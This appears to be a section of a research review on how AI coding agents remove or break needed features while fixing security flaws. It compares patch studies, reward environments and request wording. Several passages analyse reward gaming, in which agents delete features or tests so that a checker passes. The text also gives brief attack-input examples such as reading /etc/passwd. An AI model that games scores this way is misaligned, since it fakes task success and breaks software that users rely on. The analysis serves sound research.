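### Deleting old code that the program still needs

An agent deleting old code has to work out which parts the program still uses. Yuan, Zhou and colleagues (2026) tested this in *RepoClean* with 200 tasks from 34 Python projects. They took code that developers had deleted and put it back into a newer version, where it made tests fail. They told the agent that remnants of an older version were present and asked it to remove them while keeping whatever the current version needed. The best of seven models, GPT-6 Astra, got all the tests to pass in only 23% of tasks.

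How often agents broke something that worked is more relevant to lost features. Yuan and colleagues could measure this in 113 tasks, because every test file was already failing in the other 87. The seven models attempted these 113 tasks 791 times in total, and in 115 of those attempts (15%), a test file that had passed before the agent's edits failed afterwards. In 72 of the 115, the agent also got at least one failing test file to pass.

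Not all of this damage was deletion, since an agent can also break a function by editing it badly. But there was a clear case of deletion in explainshell, a program that explains shell commands, where Kimi K3 removed a method that the current version still required. It then wrote a test to check that the method was absent, and the test passed. A project test that called the method failed, but the agent couldn't have run it, because Yuan and colleagues had hidden the tests they used for scoring.

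The agent's test could show only that the deletion had worked, not whether the program needed the method, which was the point in doubt. A reviewer could easily take a passing test like this in a pull request as evidence that the change was safe. The test would also fail if anyone later restored the method.

Agents deleted much less when the instructions didn't mention old code. For 40 of the tasks, Yuan and colleagues replaced the cleanup request with a general request to find and fix the problem. GPT-6.1 Sol then removed 37% of the obsolete lines in an average task, down from about 70%. The figures for two other models fell by 28 and 37 percentage points. At least in these projects, a broken program alone did not lead agents to delete widely. A security warning is a stronger prompt than a broken program because it identifies a particular line as dangerous.

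*How Much Do Coding Agents Over-Edit, and Why?* (Goel, Steenhoek and Hu, 2026) measures unneeded edits in general. The researchers took successful patches, undid one block of changes at a time, and counted the block as unneeded if the task's tests still passed. On SWE-bench Verified, 11% of the code blocks in an average agent patch were unneeded, compared with about 14% in the developers' own patches. The 11% is a poor guide to how often agents delete features, because a harmless redundant check would count as unneeded just as the deletion of an untested feature would.

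### Agents that add too little security

In *The Security Decisions Claude Code and Codex Make*, Ong and Vikati (2026) found little sign that coding agents add protections without being asked, as they presumably would if they were overcautious by nature. Claude Code, running Opus 4.6, and OpenAI's coding agent Codex, running GPT-5.4, each built the same web application three times in each of two web frameworks, for 12 sessions in total. Six prompts asked for logins, file uploads, search, admin functions, webhooks and a production setup, but left most security choices open. Ong and Vikati then ran 33 tests against each finished application, many of them simulated attacks.

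The agents didn't limit repeated login attempts in any of the 12 sessions, nor did they add the standard security headers, which tell browsers to apply extra protections. In nine sessions, a user could register with the password "a". With the FastAPI framework, both agents left a full description of the application's endpoints public, even after a prompt to configure the application for production. An overcautious agent might well have disabled public access to it.

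The agents did pay attention to security. Every session blocked file names that point outside the upload folder and avoided revealing which email addresses had accounts. Ong and Vikati caution that the result on login limits "should be read narrowly", because many companies enforce such limits outside the application. They are most confident in the conclusion that "these agents are literal".

These models were older than Wynter's largest two, and the sessions tested what agents add to new code, so they don't show how often agents delete things. They are still evidence against treating overcaution as a constant trait. An agent that removes `eval` after a security warning might still leave a login page that allows unlimited guesses if nobody mentions the problem.

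### When a security alert prompts the change

The closest measurement of removal in response to a security alert gives a much higher rate than Wynter's. In *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation*, Lunghi, Djire and colleagues (2026) had three models write Python programs while the static scanner Semgrep checked the code after each line. In one of their setups, when Semgrep raised an alert, the harness deleted the flagged line and everything after it, then added the alert and a recommendation to the prompt. The model continued from there. The prompt instructed the model to follow a recommendation only if it didn't conflict with the task.

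One set of tasks required a web server to listen on the address 0.0.0.0, meaning it accepts connections through any of the machine's network interfaces. Semgrep flags this setting because it can expose a server to outsiders. The models dropped the required setting in 79 of 83 cases (95%). A server changed this way typically can't be reached from other machines. Dropping a required setting after a security alert comes very close to a safety-motivated removal.

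The setup probably raised the rate. The harness had already deleted the line, so the model only had to avoid writing it again. If the model did write it again, another alert could send the program back, up to five times. The result also covers only one scanner rule and small or medium-sized models that wrote one file at a time. A coding agent could have searched the project for the reason behind the setting.

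Other alerts in the same experiment had very different results. For alerts about `eval`, DeepSeek-V4.1-flash replaced an insecure program with a working, secure one in 21 of 33 cases, and it never broke a program that would otherwise have worked. The older Qwen2.5-72B managed this in 2 of 63 cases and broke the program in 23. Lunghi and colleagues attribute the failures to the difficulty of rebuilding the surrounding code after removing `eval`. When Semgrep flagged web requests to addresses the program computed at runtime, DeepSeek kept the code in 53% of cases. Many of the tasks called for such requests, so keeping them was often correct.

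Wynter's 10% to 35% and this 95% can't be soundly combined into one rate for safety-motivated removals. Wynter's rate would probably be lower for old, well-tested features, and a security alert might raise it again, but nobody has measured either effect in a coding agent. Lost function may not be the usual way security fixes fail, since the patches in *Why LLMs Fail* (2026) scored much higher on function than on security. To measure the rate directly, researchers would have to plant security flaws in established features, ask agents to fix them, and count deletions, including those that leave the file in place, separately from other broken patches.

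## How often do security fixes break what the software is for?

In two 2026 studies of AI-written security patches, about four in ten patches that closed a security hole also broke or wrongly changed something else the program did. A third study from the same year found almost no such patches. Much of the difference probably comes from how the researchers checked whether the programs still worked. None of the three studies was designed to count removed features, and a patch can damage a program in many other ways, so the share of patches that removed a feature for the sake of safety could be far below four in ten.

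### Why one kind of test isn't enough

A security test passes only if a known attack no longer works. Deleting the attacked feature will usually pass it, so researchers also need functionality tests, which pass only if legitimate behaviour still works. With both, a patch for the reporting tool's formulas can have four outcomes:

| | Functionality tests pass | Functionality tests fail |
|---|---|---|
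| Security tests pass | A restricted evaluator computes `revenue - refunds` and refuses the attack | Formula columns go blank, and the attack fails |
| Security tests fail | Formulas work, but the patch blocks only the text `/etc/passwd`, so an attacker reads a different file | The patch rejects every formula with a minus sign, and an attacker can still read files |

A good security test fails on the vulnerable version of a program and passes on the developers' fixed version. A good functionality test passes on both versions, because it covers behaviour that the developers kept. Often neither kind of test exists. Many of the real fixes in *cve bench*, a set of 20 repair tasks, came with no tests, so an AI model wrote the security tests.

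*PATCHEVAL* (Wei, Zeng and colleagues, 2025) ran both kinds of test on repairs of 230 vulnerabilities in Python, JavaScript and Go programs. The best system repaired 53 of them (23.0%). The paper also tried two ways to judge a patch without running tests. Comparing it with the developers' own fix was misleading, since a patch can look similar but leave the vulnerability in place, and a correct patch can look different. AI models' verdicts were also unreliable, because the models never ran the code and often misjudged patches because of superficial similarities.

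Testing a fix against a single attack is a weak test of security. *PatchBench* describes an agent's repair to mruby, a small implementation of the Ruby language. The mruby compiler sometimes packed a method's arguments wrongly, which caused a crash later. The agent added a check at the point of the crash. This stopped the reported attack, but a similar call on arrays still caused the same memory error, and some calls ran without an error but used the wrong arguments.

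The top three agents in *PatchBench* stopped the original attack in more than 97% of the benchmark's 213 tasks. Their success rates fell to between 75% and 82% when the patches also had to stop additional attacks, and to roughly 50% when the patched program also had to behave properly on harmless inputs. To check behaviour, the researchers ran the project's unit tests and compared the program's state after each harmless input with that of a correctly repaired copy. Around a third of the patches that withstood every attack failed this check.

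### 1Password's six difficult vulnerabilities

FLAWED, the August 2026 study by 1Password, covered six serious vulnerabilities in the Linux kernel, the Chrome browser, the mail server Exim, the messaging system ActiveMQ, Google's coding agent Gemini CLI, and Spring AI, a toolkit for adding AI models to Java programs. In *Frontier Models’ Vulnerability Patches are Often F.L.A.W.E.D*, Mierczuk, Michaels and Hoodlet explain that they wanted vulnerabilities that were too recent to be in the models' training data and whose real fixes had touched several files, functions or code paths. Most warnings from a static scanner are probably easier to fix than these.

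OpenAI's GPT-5.5 and Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.8 each made 540 attempts per vulnerability, 20 for every combination of nine prompts and three setups. In one setup the model had a single try, in another it could revise its patch using a validator, and in the third it could explore freely. Some prompts deliberately included wrong information about the cause or the fix. 1Password excluded 400 of the 6,480 attempts because the model had apparently gone looking for the real patch, and sorted the other 6,080:

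| Outcome | Share of patches |
|---|---|
| Closed the hole and kept the program's behaviour | 26.0% |
| Closed the hole but wrongly changed behaviour | 20.1% |
| Left the hole open, added a new vulnerability, or both | 53.9% |

The first two groups, the patches that closed the hole without opening another, make up 46.1% of all patches. About 44% of them (20.1 of the 46.1 percentage points) wrongly changed the program's behaviour.

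The rate of lost features must be lower than that, because not every change of behaviour removes a feature. The patches that rejected valid input may have removed a feature for some users, but other patches only changed how the program reads expressions, or replaced an allowlist with a denylist, which usually lets more through.

CyberScoop's *More than half of AI-generated patches are broken* gave the models' success rate as 47%. That is close to the combined share of the first two groups, so the article probably counted patches that broke legitimate behaviour as successes.

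The Spring AI vulnerability is a lot like the reporting tool's formulas, since an attacker could get text into an evaluator that runs expressions. A correct fix would replace the evaluator with a restricted one. Both models often escaped selected characters instead, marking them so that the evaluator treats them as ordinary text. Escaping may stop the known attack, but a differently written one might still reach the unsafe evaluator. 1Password found fragile repairs of this general kind in more than a third of the patches it had counted as closing the vulnerability. An agent that blanks the formula column makes the opposite mistake by removing the unsafe evaluator without replacing it.

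The share of clean fixes rose to 31% when a prompt contained only vetted, correct guidance, and fell to 15% when the guidance about the cause or the fix was incorrect. According to *AI生成の“修正パッチ”、4回に3回は「欠陥あり」 1PasswordがChatGPT＆Claudeで6080件検証* (山下, 2026), a Japanese news report on the study, models produced a clean fix 24.7% of the time without any suggested fix, but 7.4% of the time with a plausible but wrong one. A scanner's bad advice, such as replacing the formulas' `eval` with `ast.literal_eval`, could plausibly have a similar effect.

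### How far to trust FLAWED's grades

The 26.0% and 20.1% figures depend on grades from the two models under test. Each model graded its own patches in a fresh session and also graded the other model's patches, and the study averaged the results. The graders used the developers' real fix as their reference.

flyingpenguin's *Disinformation Pushed by 1Password* (2026) attacks this method. The post is a polemic that accuses the company of deliberate deception, but its main points come from figures in the paper. The automated grades matched the researchers' own review only 65.9% of the time. For the Linux vulnerability, the reference fix itself contained a bug that the kernel's maintainers corrected one commit later. Of 783 patches for that vulnerability, 248 reproduced the bug, and the graders noticed it in 24. For Chrome, the graders passed many patches that had moved the vulnerability to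 another place instead of removing it.

The errors in the Linux grades would not change the 44% much. Correcting the 224 missed cases would raise the figure to about 47% if the graders had put them all among the clean fixes, or lower it to about 39% if they had put them all among the patches that wrongly changed behaviour. The 65.9% agreement is a more serious problem, because it does not measure how often the graders confused a clean fix with one that changed behaviour. Wei and colleagues also found AI models unreliable at this kind of judgement. The 44% is therefore a rough figure.

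The security firm Trail of Bits objected that some of the test's prompts told the models to apply the wrong fix or forbade testing, and that the models ran only at their default reasoning settings. Wheeler summarises its review in *Finding and Fixing Vulnerabilities Using AI*, a guide from the Open Source Security Foundation. Trail of Bits found that 2,634 of 3,067 patches (86%) blocked the supplied exploit. It warned that this figure greatly overstates how many patches fixed the vulnerability, since blocking one exploit doesn't show that it can't be exploited another way, let alone that the program still works. Trail of Bits had a stake because it was OpenAI's partner in Patch the Planet, a patching initiative, and the FLAWED paper criticises two of the initiative's patches.

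Hussain (2026), in *FLAWED's Flaws and What This Means for Industry Research*, found arithmetic errors in FLAWED and missing citations to earlier work, and called for a correction or retraction. Hussain, who used to work at Trail of Bits herself, still wanted independent researchers to test AI companies' claims, but more carefully.

1Password updated the study on 26 October 2026. The revised paper's title limits its claim to "complex, novel vulnerabilities", and the company acknowledges that the study's constraints may have limited what the agents could produce. The main percentages stayed the same. 1Password also published feedback from Anthropic, which argued that models now generate patches faster than anyone can verify them. Anthropic recommended verifying patches by running them instead of inspecting them, with human experts as the final reviewers. Running the patches would address the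 weakest part of FLAWED, whose graders had to judge from the code whether legitimate behaviour still worked.

FLAWED also has no human baseline. Developers in a hurry break things too, as the first Linux fix showed, but the study doesn't measure whether they do so more or less often than the models.

### Repairs to software that acts on a model's output

In *Towards Demystifying and Repairing LLM-in-the-Loop Vulnerabilities*, Ma, Rong and colleagues (2026) ran functionality tests and reached a similar result. They collected 41 vulnerabilities that an attacker can exploit only through a language model inside the program. In Langroid, a toolkit for building AI agents, an attacker could get the model to write a malicious expression, which the program then evaluated as code.

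These vulnerabilities are useful for studying lost features because the dangerous operation is often the purpose of the software, so deleting it would fix the vulnerability but stop the program from doing its job. In 20 of the 41, the program ran code or expressions that a model had written, typically with `eval` or `exec`. Others involved database queries, tools the model could operate, or web content it had generated.

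Ma and colleagues wrote several variants of each attack. To check functionality, they combined each project's tests of the affected feature with new ones they wrote, and kept only those that passed on both the vulnerable and the fixed version. A repair succeeded only if it built correctly and passed every test. Five repair agents, each run with four models, made 772 attempts. Two of the agents could handle only the 35 vulnerabilities in Python projects, so they made fewer attempts than the others.

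Of those attempts, 201 succeeded and 571 failed. In 120 of the failures (21%), the patch passed the security tests but broke legitimate functions. That share ranged from 11.3% for the agent Aider to 24.8% for Agentless. In 219 other failures, the patch kept the functions working but left an attack open. Another 53 patches failed both kinds of test. The remaining failures included attempts that produced no patch or one that didn't build.

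A share of failures says little about the risk a project takes when it accepts a patch that stops the attack. For that, the 120 belong with the 201 successes, which makes 321 patches that passed the security tests. About 37% of them broke something. On this measure Aider no longer stands out:

| Agent | Patches that passed the security tests | Of those, broke legitimate functions |
|---|---|---|
| SWE-agent | 81 | 31% |
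| OpenHands | 80 | 33% |
| Aider | 46 | 33% |
| AutoCodeRover | 59 | 44% |
| Agentless | 55 | 51% |

Aider had a low share of such failures mainly because it failed so often in other ways, including 39 attempts in which it produced no patch. Only AutoCodeRover and Agentless are limited to Python, so their higher rates may partly reflect a different set of tasks.

The agents succeeded more often on the `eval` and `exec` vulnerabilities than on the others. Adding up the paper's results by category gives 135 successes in 400 attempts (34%) for the first group, against 66 in 372 (18%) for the others. Ma and colleagues suggest that the dangerous line is easy to find in such cases. They don't report the causes of failure by category, so it's unclear how often an agent broke the feature while repairing an `eval` call.

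These vulnerabilities were also harder to repair than ordinary ones in similar software. OpenHands with DeepSeek-V4-Pro repaired 17 of the 41, compared with 45 of 75 vulnerabilities in AI-related projects where the attack didn't need a model. (The paper's text swaps these two success rates, but its table is correct.) The models tested are no longer the strongest available, and GPT-4o was already old when the study appeared, so newer models may break less.

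A patch can remove part of a feature without deleting the whole feature, as one failed repair to LlamaIndex shows. LlamaIndex, a toolkit that connects language models to data, let a model write database queries and passed them directly to the database program SQLite. SQLite's `ATTACH DATABASE` command opens another database file and creates it if it doesn't exist, so an attacker could create files on the machine by getting the model to write that command.

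The agent's patch searched each query for dangerous words and refused any query that contained one. In simplified form, it worked like this:

```python
if re.search(r"\b(attach|detach)\b", query, re.IGNORECASE):
    raise ValueError("Unsafe query")
```

That stops the attack, but it also blocks `SELECT attach FROM emails`, a harmless request to read a column named "attach". Most users would notice nothing, but anyone with such a column could no longer query it. CleverAgents' list of forbidden words had the same weakness and would have blocked printing a file called `platform.txt`.

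The developers used SQLite's authorizer, a function that SQLite consults about each action a query would perform. A simplified version looks like this:

```python
def authorize(action, *details):
    if action == sqlite3.SQLITE_ATTACH:
        return sqlite3.SQLITE_DENY
    return sqlite3.SQLITE_OK

connection.set_authorizer(authorize)
```

SQLite interprets the query before calling this function. It classifies reading a column called "attach" as a read, which the function allows, and opening another database as an attach, which the function blocks however the attacker spells or spaces the command. The fix is only a few lines longer than the word search, but whoever writes it has to know that SQLite offers this hook.

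### A study that found almost no such trade-off

*Why LLMs Fail* reports very different results. One of Google's Gemini Flash models wrote five patches for each of 64 vulnerabilities in Java projects, and 319 of the 320 patches were usable for the analysis. The model received the vulnerable code and the type of vulnerability and returned corrected code in a single reply, rather than working as an agent. The prompt included an instruction to preserve all original functionality.

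| Outcome | Patches |
|---|---|
| Passed both kinds of test | 79 |
| Closed the hole but broke a functionality test | 1 |
| Passed the functionality tests but left the hole open | 33 |
| Failed both | 164 |
| Didn't compile | 42 |

Only one of the 80 patches that fixed a vulnerability broke a functionality test. The model's main problem was failing to fix the vulnerability. On a scale from 0 to 1, the average scores were 0.832 for functionality and 0.251 for security.

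The study also tested for a trade-off by checking whether patches with higher security scores had lower functionality scores. A trade-off would produce a negative correlation, but the correlation was positive, at 0.267, and the paper reports it as not statistically significant. A correlation of that size across 319 patches would normally be significant, so the calculation may have used averages over fewer groups. The positive correlation is also hard to interpret because patches that didn't compile presumably scored zero on both measures, which alone would push it up.

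*Why LLMs Fail* also comes close to counting removals. It sorts failed patches by what went wrong, and four of them (1.3% of all 319 patches) "overcorrect by removing too much functionality". The other two groups have 143 and 17 patches. Together the three groups add up to the 164 patches that failed both kinds of test, so it seems that none of the four removals fixed the vulnerability.

This count can't include removals that no test detected. A patch that stopped the attack but deleted an untested feature would be among the 79 successes.

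### Why the results differ so much

The three studies are easier to compare if each one is reduced to the patches that closed the hole:

| Study | Closed the hole | Of those, broke or wrongly changed behaviour | How the study checked behaviour |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1Password | 46.1% of 6,080 | 44% | Two AI models compared the patch with the developers' fix |
| Ma and colleagues | 321 of 772 | 37% | Tests aimed at the affected feature |
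| *Why LLMs Fail* | 80 of 319 | 1% | The project's existing test suite |

Test coverage could explain much of the gap. An existing suite covers what its developers thought worth testing, which may not include the feature that a security patch affects. The reporting tool has 40 tests, but none of them cover formulas. A patch that blanks every formula column would pass all 40, and *Why LLMs Fail* would count it as correct and secure. Ma and colleagues would have looked for formula tests, written some if necessary, and recorded that the patch broke the feature.

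The average functionality score is even less sensitive to a broken feature, because it measures the share of tests that still pass relative to the developers' own fix. If the reporting tool gained a single test for formulas, the patch that blanks them would pass 40 of 41 tests and score 0.976, even though formulas would no longer work for anyone. The median score in *Why LLMs Fail* was 0.999, yet more than half of the patches failed the functionality check, which required every test to pass.

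Some of those 164 double failures may not have damaged the program. In a Java project, the test that tries the exploit can be part of the ordinary test suite. If it was here, a patch that left the hole open but broke nothing else would also have failed a "functionality" test. This would explain how so many patches failed on functionality with nearly perfect scores.

1Password's graders could have overcounted breakage, because they weren't limited to behaviour covered by a test and could object to small changes that no user would notice. They could also have missed serious changes.

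Functionality scores also varied by type of vulnerability. In *Why LLMs Fail*, patches for infinite loops averaged 0.999. Users don't need infinite loops, so fixing one takes nothing away from them. Patches for a flaw in how programs read XML, a common data format, averaged only 0.631. An XML file can tell the program to load other files, which attackers exploit to read private data, and the usual repair is to switch that ability off. One in five of the XML patches didn't compile, which explains part of the low score, but even if those all scored zero, the rest averaged only about 0.79. The sample is only 25 patches, but the result fits the idea that fixes harm functionality more when the dangerous operation is itself a feature.

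The reporting tool's formulas, export hook and webhooks are all features of that sort. For them, the 37% from Ma and colleagues is probably a better guide than the 1%, because half of the vulnerabilities they studied involved running code or expressions, and they tested the feature at risk. But the 37% is a rate of broken functions under older models, and it includes partial losses, such as the rejected "attach" queries, along with any outright removals.

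## Why would an agent choose removal?

There are four plausible explanations for an agent deleting a feature that it could have repaired:

- A check rewards the absence of the flagged code.
- The request doesn't state what has to keep working.
- The agent can't see who uses the feature.
- Training has made the model cautious about certain patterns, such as `eval`.

More than one of these explanations may apply to the same deletion. The evidence is moderate for the effect of checks, suggestive for vague requests and thin for unseen users. It is weakest for trained caution, where some results suggest the opposite.

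### A score that favours deletion

Suppose a static scanner reports three findings in the reporting tool, one for each place that calls `eval` on a formula: the report builder, the preview page and the spreadsheet export. If the agent deletes formulas, all three findings disappear. It could instead write a restricted evaluator like Binex's, which checks a formula's syntax tree and then passes the formula to `eval`. All three places would use this function, so only one `eval` call would be left. The scanner would still report it, because it detects the call but not the check before it.

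Now suppose the agent's score is the percentage of tests that pass, minus 10 points for each remaining finding:

| Change | Findings left | Tests passed | Score |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 3 | 40 of 40 | 70 |
| Restricted evaluator | 1 | 40 of 40 | 90 |
| Formulas deleted | 0 | 40 of 40 | 100 |

The agent scores 10 points lower if it keeps the formulas. Adding enough formula tests can reverse this. With four, deletion passes 40 of 44 tests and scores 90.9, still ahead of the evaluator. A fifth lowers deletion's score to 88.9, which puts it behind. If the score were zero unless every test passed, a single formula test would be enough to remove deletion's advantage.

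The handwritten evaluator from earlier, which never calls `eval`, would also score 100. Deleting the feature would then score no higher, but it would still be much less work.

Wynter calls deletion "the shortest route to a clean review" and compares it with other cases in which coding agents satisfied only the literal terms of an objective, such as by deleting failing tests or hard-coding the expected outputs. Wynter's experiment provides the strongest evidence for any of the four explanations. Removals fell sharply when the checker was changed to also report deleted files, with the rest of the setup unchanged.

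That result is ambiguous, though, because the deletion check both made removal count as a problem and showed the agents that the missing file mattered. They may have been avoiding a bad outcome, or they may have learned something about what the project needed. Also, the defects broke project rules rather than creating security holes.

### Do published scoring systems penalise `eval`?

Developers can train coding agents by reinforcement learning. The model attempts tasks, and training makes it more likely to repeat behaviour that earns a high reward. An environment is the software that sets the tasks and computes the reward.

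*Codebase Navigation Repair OpenEnv*, by Chirag0123, is a small public environment where an agent explores an unfamiliar Python project, edits it and runs its tests. The environment searches whatever the agent writes to a file and flags patterns that include `eval`, calls to `subprocess` and web requests. Each flag takes 0.15 off a security score that starts at 1 and makes up 10% of the overall grade, so it lowers the overall grade by 0.015. A separate count of violations can lower the grade a little more.

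The share of passing tests makes up 30% of the grade. In a project with 40 tests, like the reporting tool, failing one test lowers the grade by 0.0075, half as much as one flag does.

The safe version of the export hook, with its fixed list of commands, would get the same two flags as the dangerous version with `shell=True`, one for importing `subprocess` and another for calling it. Together, the flags would lower the score by 0.03, as much as failing four of the 40 tests. An agent that deleted the hook would get no flags, so it would score higher than one that kept it, even if three tests failed as a result.

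But the search covers only what the agent writes, so the agent isn't penalized for leaving the dangerous hook untouched either. The scoring therefore discourages repair more than it encourages deletion. The environment reports this grade separately from the reward for each step, so someone could train an agent there without using the grade.

A coding environment from Meta gives a reward of −1.0 if the agent's code contains `eval(`, `exec(`, `open(` or `__import__`, or imports `os` or `subprocess`, and 0 otherwise. A second rule adds 0.1 for code of up to 100 characters and subtracts 0.2 for code with a syntax error. Neither rule depends on whether the program completes the task, so an empty program earns the highest reward.

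The first rule matches the characters `eval(` anywhere in the text, so it also penalises `ast.literal_eval(`, which Bandit recommends as safer, and comments like `# replaced eval() with a parser`.

Meta's *Python Code Action Environment* applies both rules by default at every step, but it scores programs that the agent runs, not changes to an existing project. Hugging Face's *Coding Environment* describes Meta's environment as suited to testing infrastructure and demonstrating how such environments work. Meta's environment shows how easily a pattern match can become a reward, but it isn't evidence that any commercial coding agent learned from such a reward.

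An environment by DeepSource, a company that sells code-checking tools, comes closer to real security work. The agent has to fix a recently published vulnerability in a Go library that lets attackers reach files outside a permitted folder. The default weights, which the company calls illustrative, are:

| What the environment measures | Weight |
|---|---|
| The checker for this vulnerability stops firing | 0.40 |
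| No new problems | 0.25 |
| Regression tests pass | 0.20 |
| Overall code quality | 0.10 |
| Small diff | 0.05 |

DeepSource ran ten models in this environment and got 29 usable attempts. All 29 silenced the checker, but in two of them, both by GPT-5.3-Codex, the attack still worked. The tests caught these two, but each scored about 0.80. An attempt that fixed the vulnerability but still triggered the checker could have scored 0.60 at most.

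By the same arithmetic, an agent that deleted a feature and failed the tests could score about 0.80, well above the score for a sound repair that the checker didn't recognise. The agent might even pass the tests, because DeepSource adapted them from the published attack, which wouldn't work on a deleted feature. But DeepSource doesn't report any deletions, and 27 of the 29 attempts passed the tests. DeepSource also only measured these models and didn't train them, so the two bad fixes don't show what a model would learn from the reward.

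Environments can guard against agents removing needed features. *CyberSecurity_OWASP*, by Humanlearning, plants one authorization flaw in a generated web application and scores the repair partly with hidden tests. Some of those tests check that pages meant for the public are still public, so an agent that secured the application by closing everything would fail them.

Another option is to have a person judge each finding before the agent acts on it. With Replit's *Agent security scans*, the user reads the report first and can dismiss findings they "understand and accept", or revise a finding before the agent works on it. OpenAI's *Security scanners with Agents SDK*, an example built on the scanners Semgrep and Bandit, also treats findings as candidates to check and has a person approve any fix. In the reporting tool, somebody who knew about the syntax check could dismiss the last `eval` finding,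 and the restricted evaluator would then also score 100.

Replit's last step is to rerun the scan to verify that the issues are resolved. On its own, that scan would pass whether the agent repaired the code or deleted it.

### What "make this secure" leaves out

A request such as "make this secure" leaves at least three decisions to the agent.

The right safeguard depends partly on the threat model, meaning who might attack and what they could already do. If the only people who can type formulas are two administrators who can log in to the server anyway, `eval` gives them little new power. If any employee can type formulas, the tool needs a restricted evaluator. If the public can, it also needs limits on computing time, so that nobody can tie up the server with `9**9**9`.

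The request also omits the permitted users. The admin endpoint should still work for administrators and the nightly script, but an agent with no information about the script could easily lock it out.

Finally, the request doesn't specify which losses are acceptable. The owners might not mind if a few unusual formulas stopped working or all formulas were off for a day, but they would mind losing them for good. An agent told to "make this secure" would plainly fail if it left a hole open, but it could delete formulas and arguably still have done what it was asked.

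A better request for the formulas would be:

> Any employee can type a formula, and the tool runs it with `eval`. An attacker who has stolen one employee's password must not be able to use a formula to read files, run commands or tie up the server. Finance needs column names, arithmetic, brackets and `round`, and saved formulas that use only these must give the same results as before. Other formulas may stop working, but they must show a clear error. Don't remove or disable formulas. If you can't meet these conditions, explain why and ask before changing anything.

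This takes a few minutes to write, and the writer has to know what finance uses.

Some published guidance covers part of this. According to OpenAI's guide to security scans with Codex, useful guidance names the inputs an attacker controls, the trust boundaries and the sensitive actions. The prompt in Cursor's *Scan codebase for vulnerabilities* tells the agent to find vulnerabilities "with a real end-to-end attack path". It lists shell execution and webhooks as places to look, not as faults. Instructions like these should reduce false alarms, but they describe only the threat. An agent that has confirmed a real attack on the formulas still needs to know what finance can't do without.

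There is some evidence that the wording of a request affects how much code agents delete. When Yuan and colleagues replaced a request to clean up old code with a general request to fix the problem, agents deleted far fewer obsolete lines. That experiment didn't involve security, and the agents were supposed to delete those lines.

When Wynter asked the three models to review correct pull requests and fix any problems, all three usually edited the code anyway. When the request was instead to fix a checker's findings, and there were none, they changed nothing in 75 runs. Either the narrower request or the empty list of findings could explain the difference, and Wynter notes that the experiment can't separate them.

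A vague request doesn't always lead an agent to remove needed features. Maynard's one-line prompt specified almost nothing, yet the agent kept every feature he describes.

### Users the agent can't see

An agent working on the reporting tool can find the code that calls `column_value`, but the formulas are in a database and the people who read the margins are in the finance department. Nothing in the repository shows whether finance uses a feature every month or everybody has forgotten it. This lack of information fits the pattern of the invented examples well, but there is no experiment that gives some agents a list of a feature's users, withholds it from others, and compares how often each group deletes the feature.

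In Wynter's experiment, agents made much better repairs when they were told which project rule a change had broken and where. The gains were largest for rules that the code didn't reveal. But without the deletion check, Sonnet still removed features almost as often as when it worked alone. This may be because knowing what is wrong with code doesn't tell an agent whether anyone needs it.

A partial list of users could also mislead an agent. In one of Wynter's pull requests, a change to a shared function had broken four calls to it, but the checker reported only one. In four of five runs, Haiku fixed that call and stopped. Without the checker, it had repaired all four calls every time. The two larger models avoided this mistake by giving the function a default value, which fixed all the calls at once. Similarly, a small model told only that finance uses formulas might protect finance's formulas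 and break the operations team's.

### Has training made agents wary of certain code?

If training made a model likely to avoid `eval`, an agent might remove it even when no scanner is running and nobody has mentioned security. For example, it might delete the formulas while changing the date format in the same file.

Researchers train models in ways that could teach them to remove needed features. *Learning to Generate Secure Code via Token-Level Rewards* (2026) attaches rewards to individual tokens, the small pieces of text a model produces, to "explicitly reinforce defensive coding patterns". *SecureCodeRL* (2026) rewards programs for passing tests and subtracts a penalty for findings from the security scanner Bandit. A model trained this second way could get a higher reward by learning safer replacements for dangerous calls. It could also learn to avoid those calls where a task needs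 them, unless a test covers the need.

According to *Secure Code Generation via Online Reinforcement Learning with Vulnerability Reward Model* (2026), existing methods of training models to write secure code often make the code substantially less useful, and developers reject code that doesn't work. This is the closest evidence that agents remove features because training made them cautious, but it concerns newly written programs. A program can fail for many reasons besides leaving out a dangerous call, and the finding doesn't show that a model trained this way would delete a feature from someone else's project.

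Other results suggest that agents don't have a general habit of caution. The agents that Ong and Vikati tested left login attempts unlimited when nobody asked for a limit. In the experiment by Lunghi and colleagues, models almost always dropped a required network setting after an alert, but DeepSeek often kept web requests that the scanner had flagged. A model could still avoid a few specific patterns, and `eval` is an obvious candidate because so much security advice warns against it. Or the alert alone may cause the removals. To distinguish between these explanations, researchers would have to look at edits made without an alert.

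### What OpenAI and Anthropic ask of their agents

Both companies publish rules or tools that should indirectly discourage careless removal. OpenAI's Model Spec describes how its models should behave, and the October 2025 version lists ways to reduce the harm from a model's mistakes, including controlling side effects, expressing uncertainty and staying within bounds (OpenAI, 2025). OpenAI's *Our approach to the Model Spec* adds that an agent with incomplete instructions should fill in the details itself "while carefully controlling real-world side effects".

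It isn't obvious how this applies to the formulas. Deleting them from a branch doesn't affect finance until somebody merges the change and installs the new version. An agent could reasonably treat the deletion as a draft and leave it to the reviewer to object. It could also treat the loss of a monthly report as a side effect it should avoid.

According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, Codex's Auto preset lets it read files, make edits and run commands in the working directory without asking. It needs approval to edit files elsewhere, run commands that use the network, or make tool calls labelled as destructive. An agent in this mode would therefore have to ask before downloading a package, but it could delete the export hook without asking. These rules are a sensible way to protect the developer's computer, and a developer can undo an edit to a file. But they don't protect the feature,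 because they depend on where an action takes place and not on what the software loses.

Anthropic's *Scan your codebase for vulnerabilities* describes a plugin for Claude Code that adds more steps before code is edited. Several agents map the program's architecture, build a threat model and review every finding independently. The threat model should help an agent recognise that an administrators' console is less exposed than a public form. The plugin can then turn findings into patches, but the user reviews and applies them and still has to notice if one removes something.

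An agent with good rules may still behave badly. In its June 2026 system card, which reports on tests of Claude Fable 5 and Claude Mythos 5, Anthropic rates Mythos 5 as better aligned than other developers' models but acknowledges that it still sometimes takes "reckless or destructive actions". That description covers much more than coding and gives no rate for deleted features.

Requiring an agent to ask first may work better than advising it to be careful. In an earlier study by Wynter, agents couldn't delete a file without approval, and nobody was there to give it, so they had to repair the code instead. They succeeded in 91% to 100% of runs. Wynter suggests that the approval requirement may partly explain why these results were better than in the later experiment, but the two studies used different changes and the earlier one used an older Sonnet model. The requirement also wouldn't have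 stopped an agent from blanking the formulas, because that takes only an edit.

### An experiment that could separate the causes

None of the experiments above changed only a security instruction and then measured the lost functionality. Wynter changed the deletion check, Yuan and colleagues changed a request about old code, and 1Password changed the technical guidance about a vulnerability. The experiments therefore don't show how much of a safety-motivated removal comes from the word "security" and how much from the check, the missing information or the model's training.

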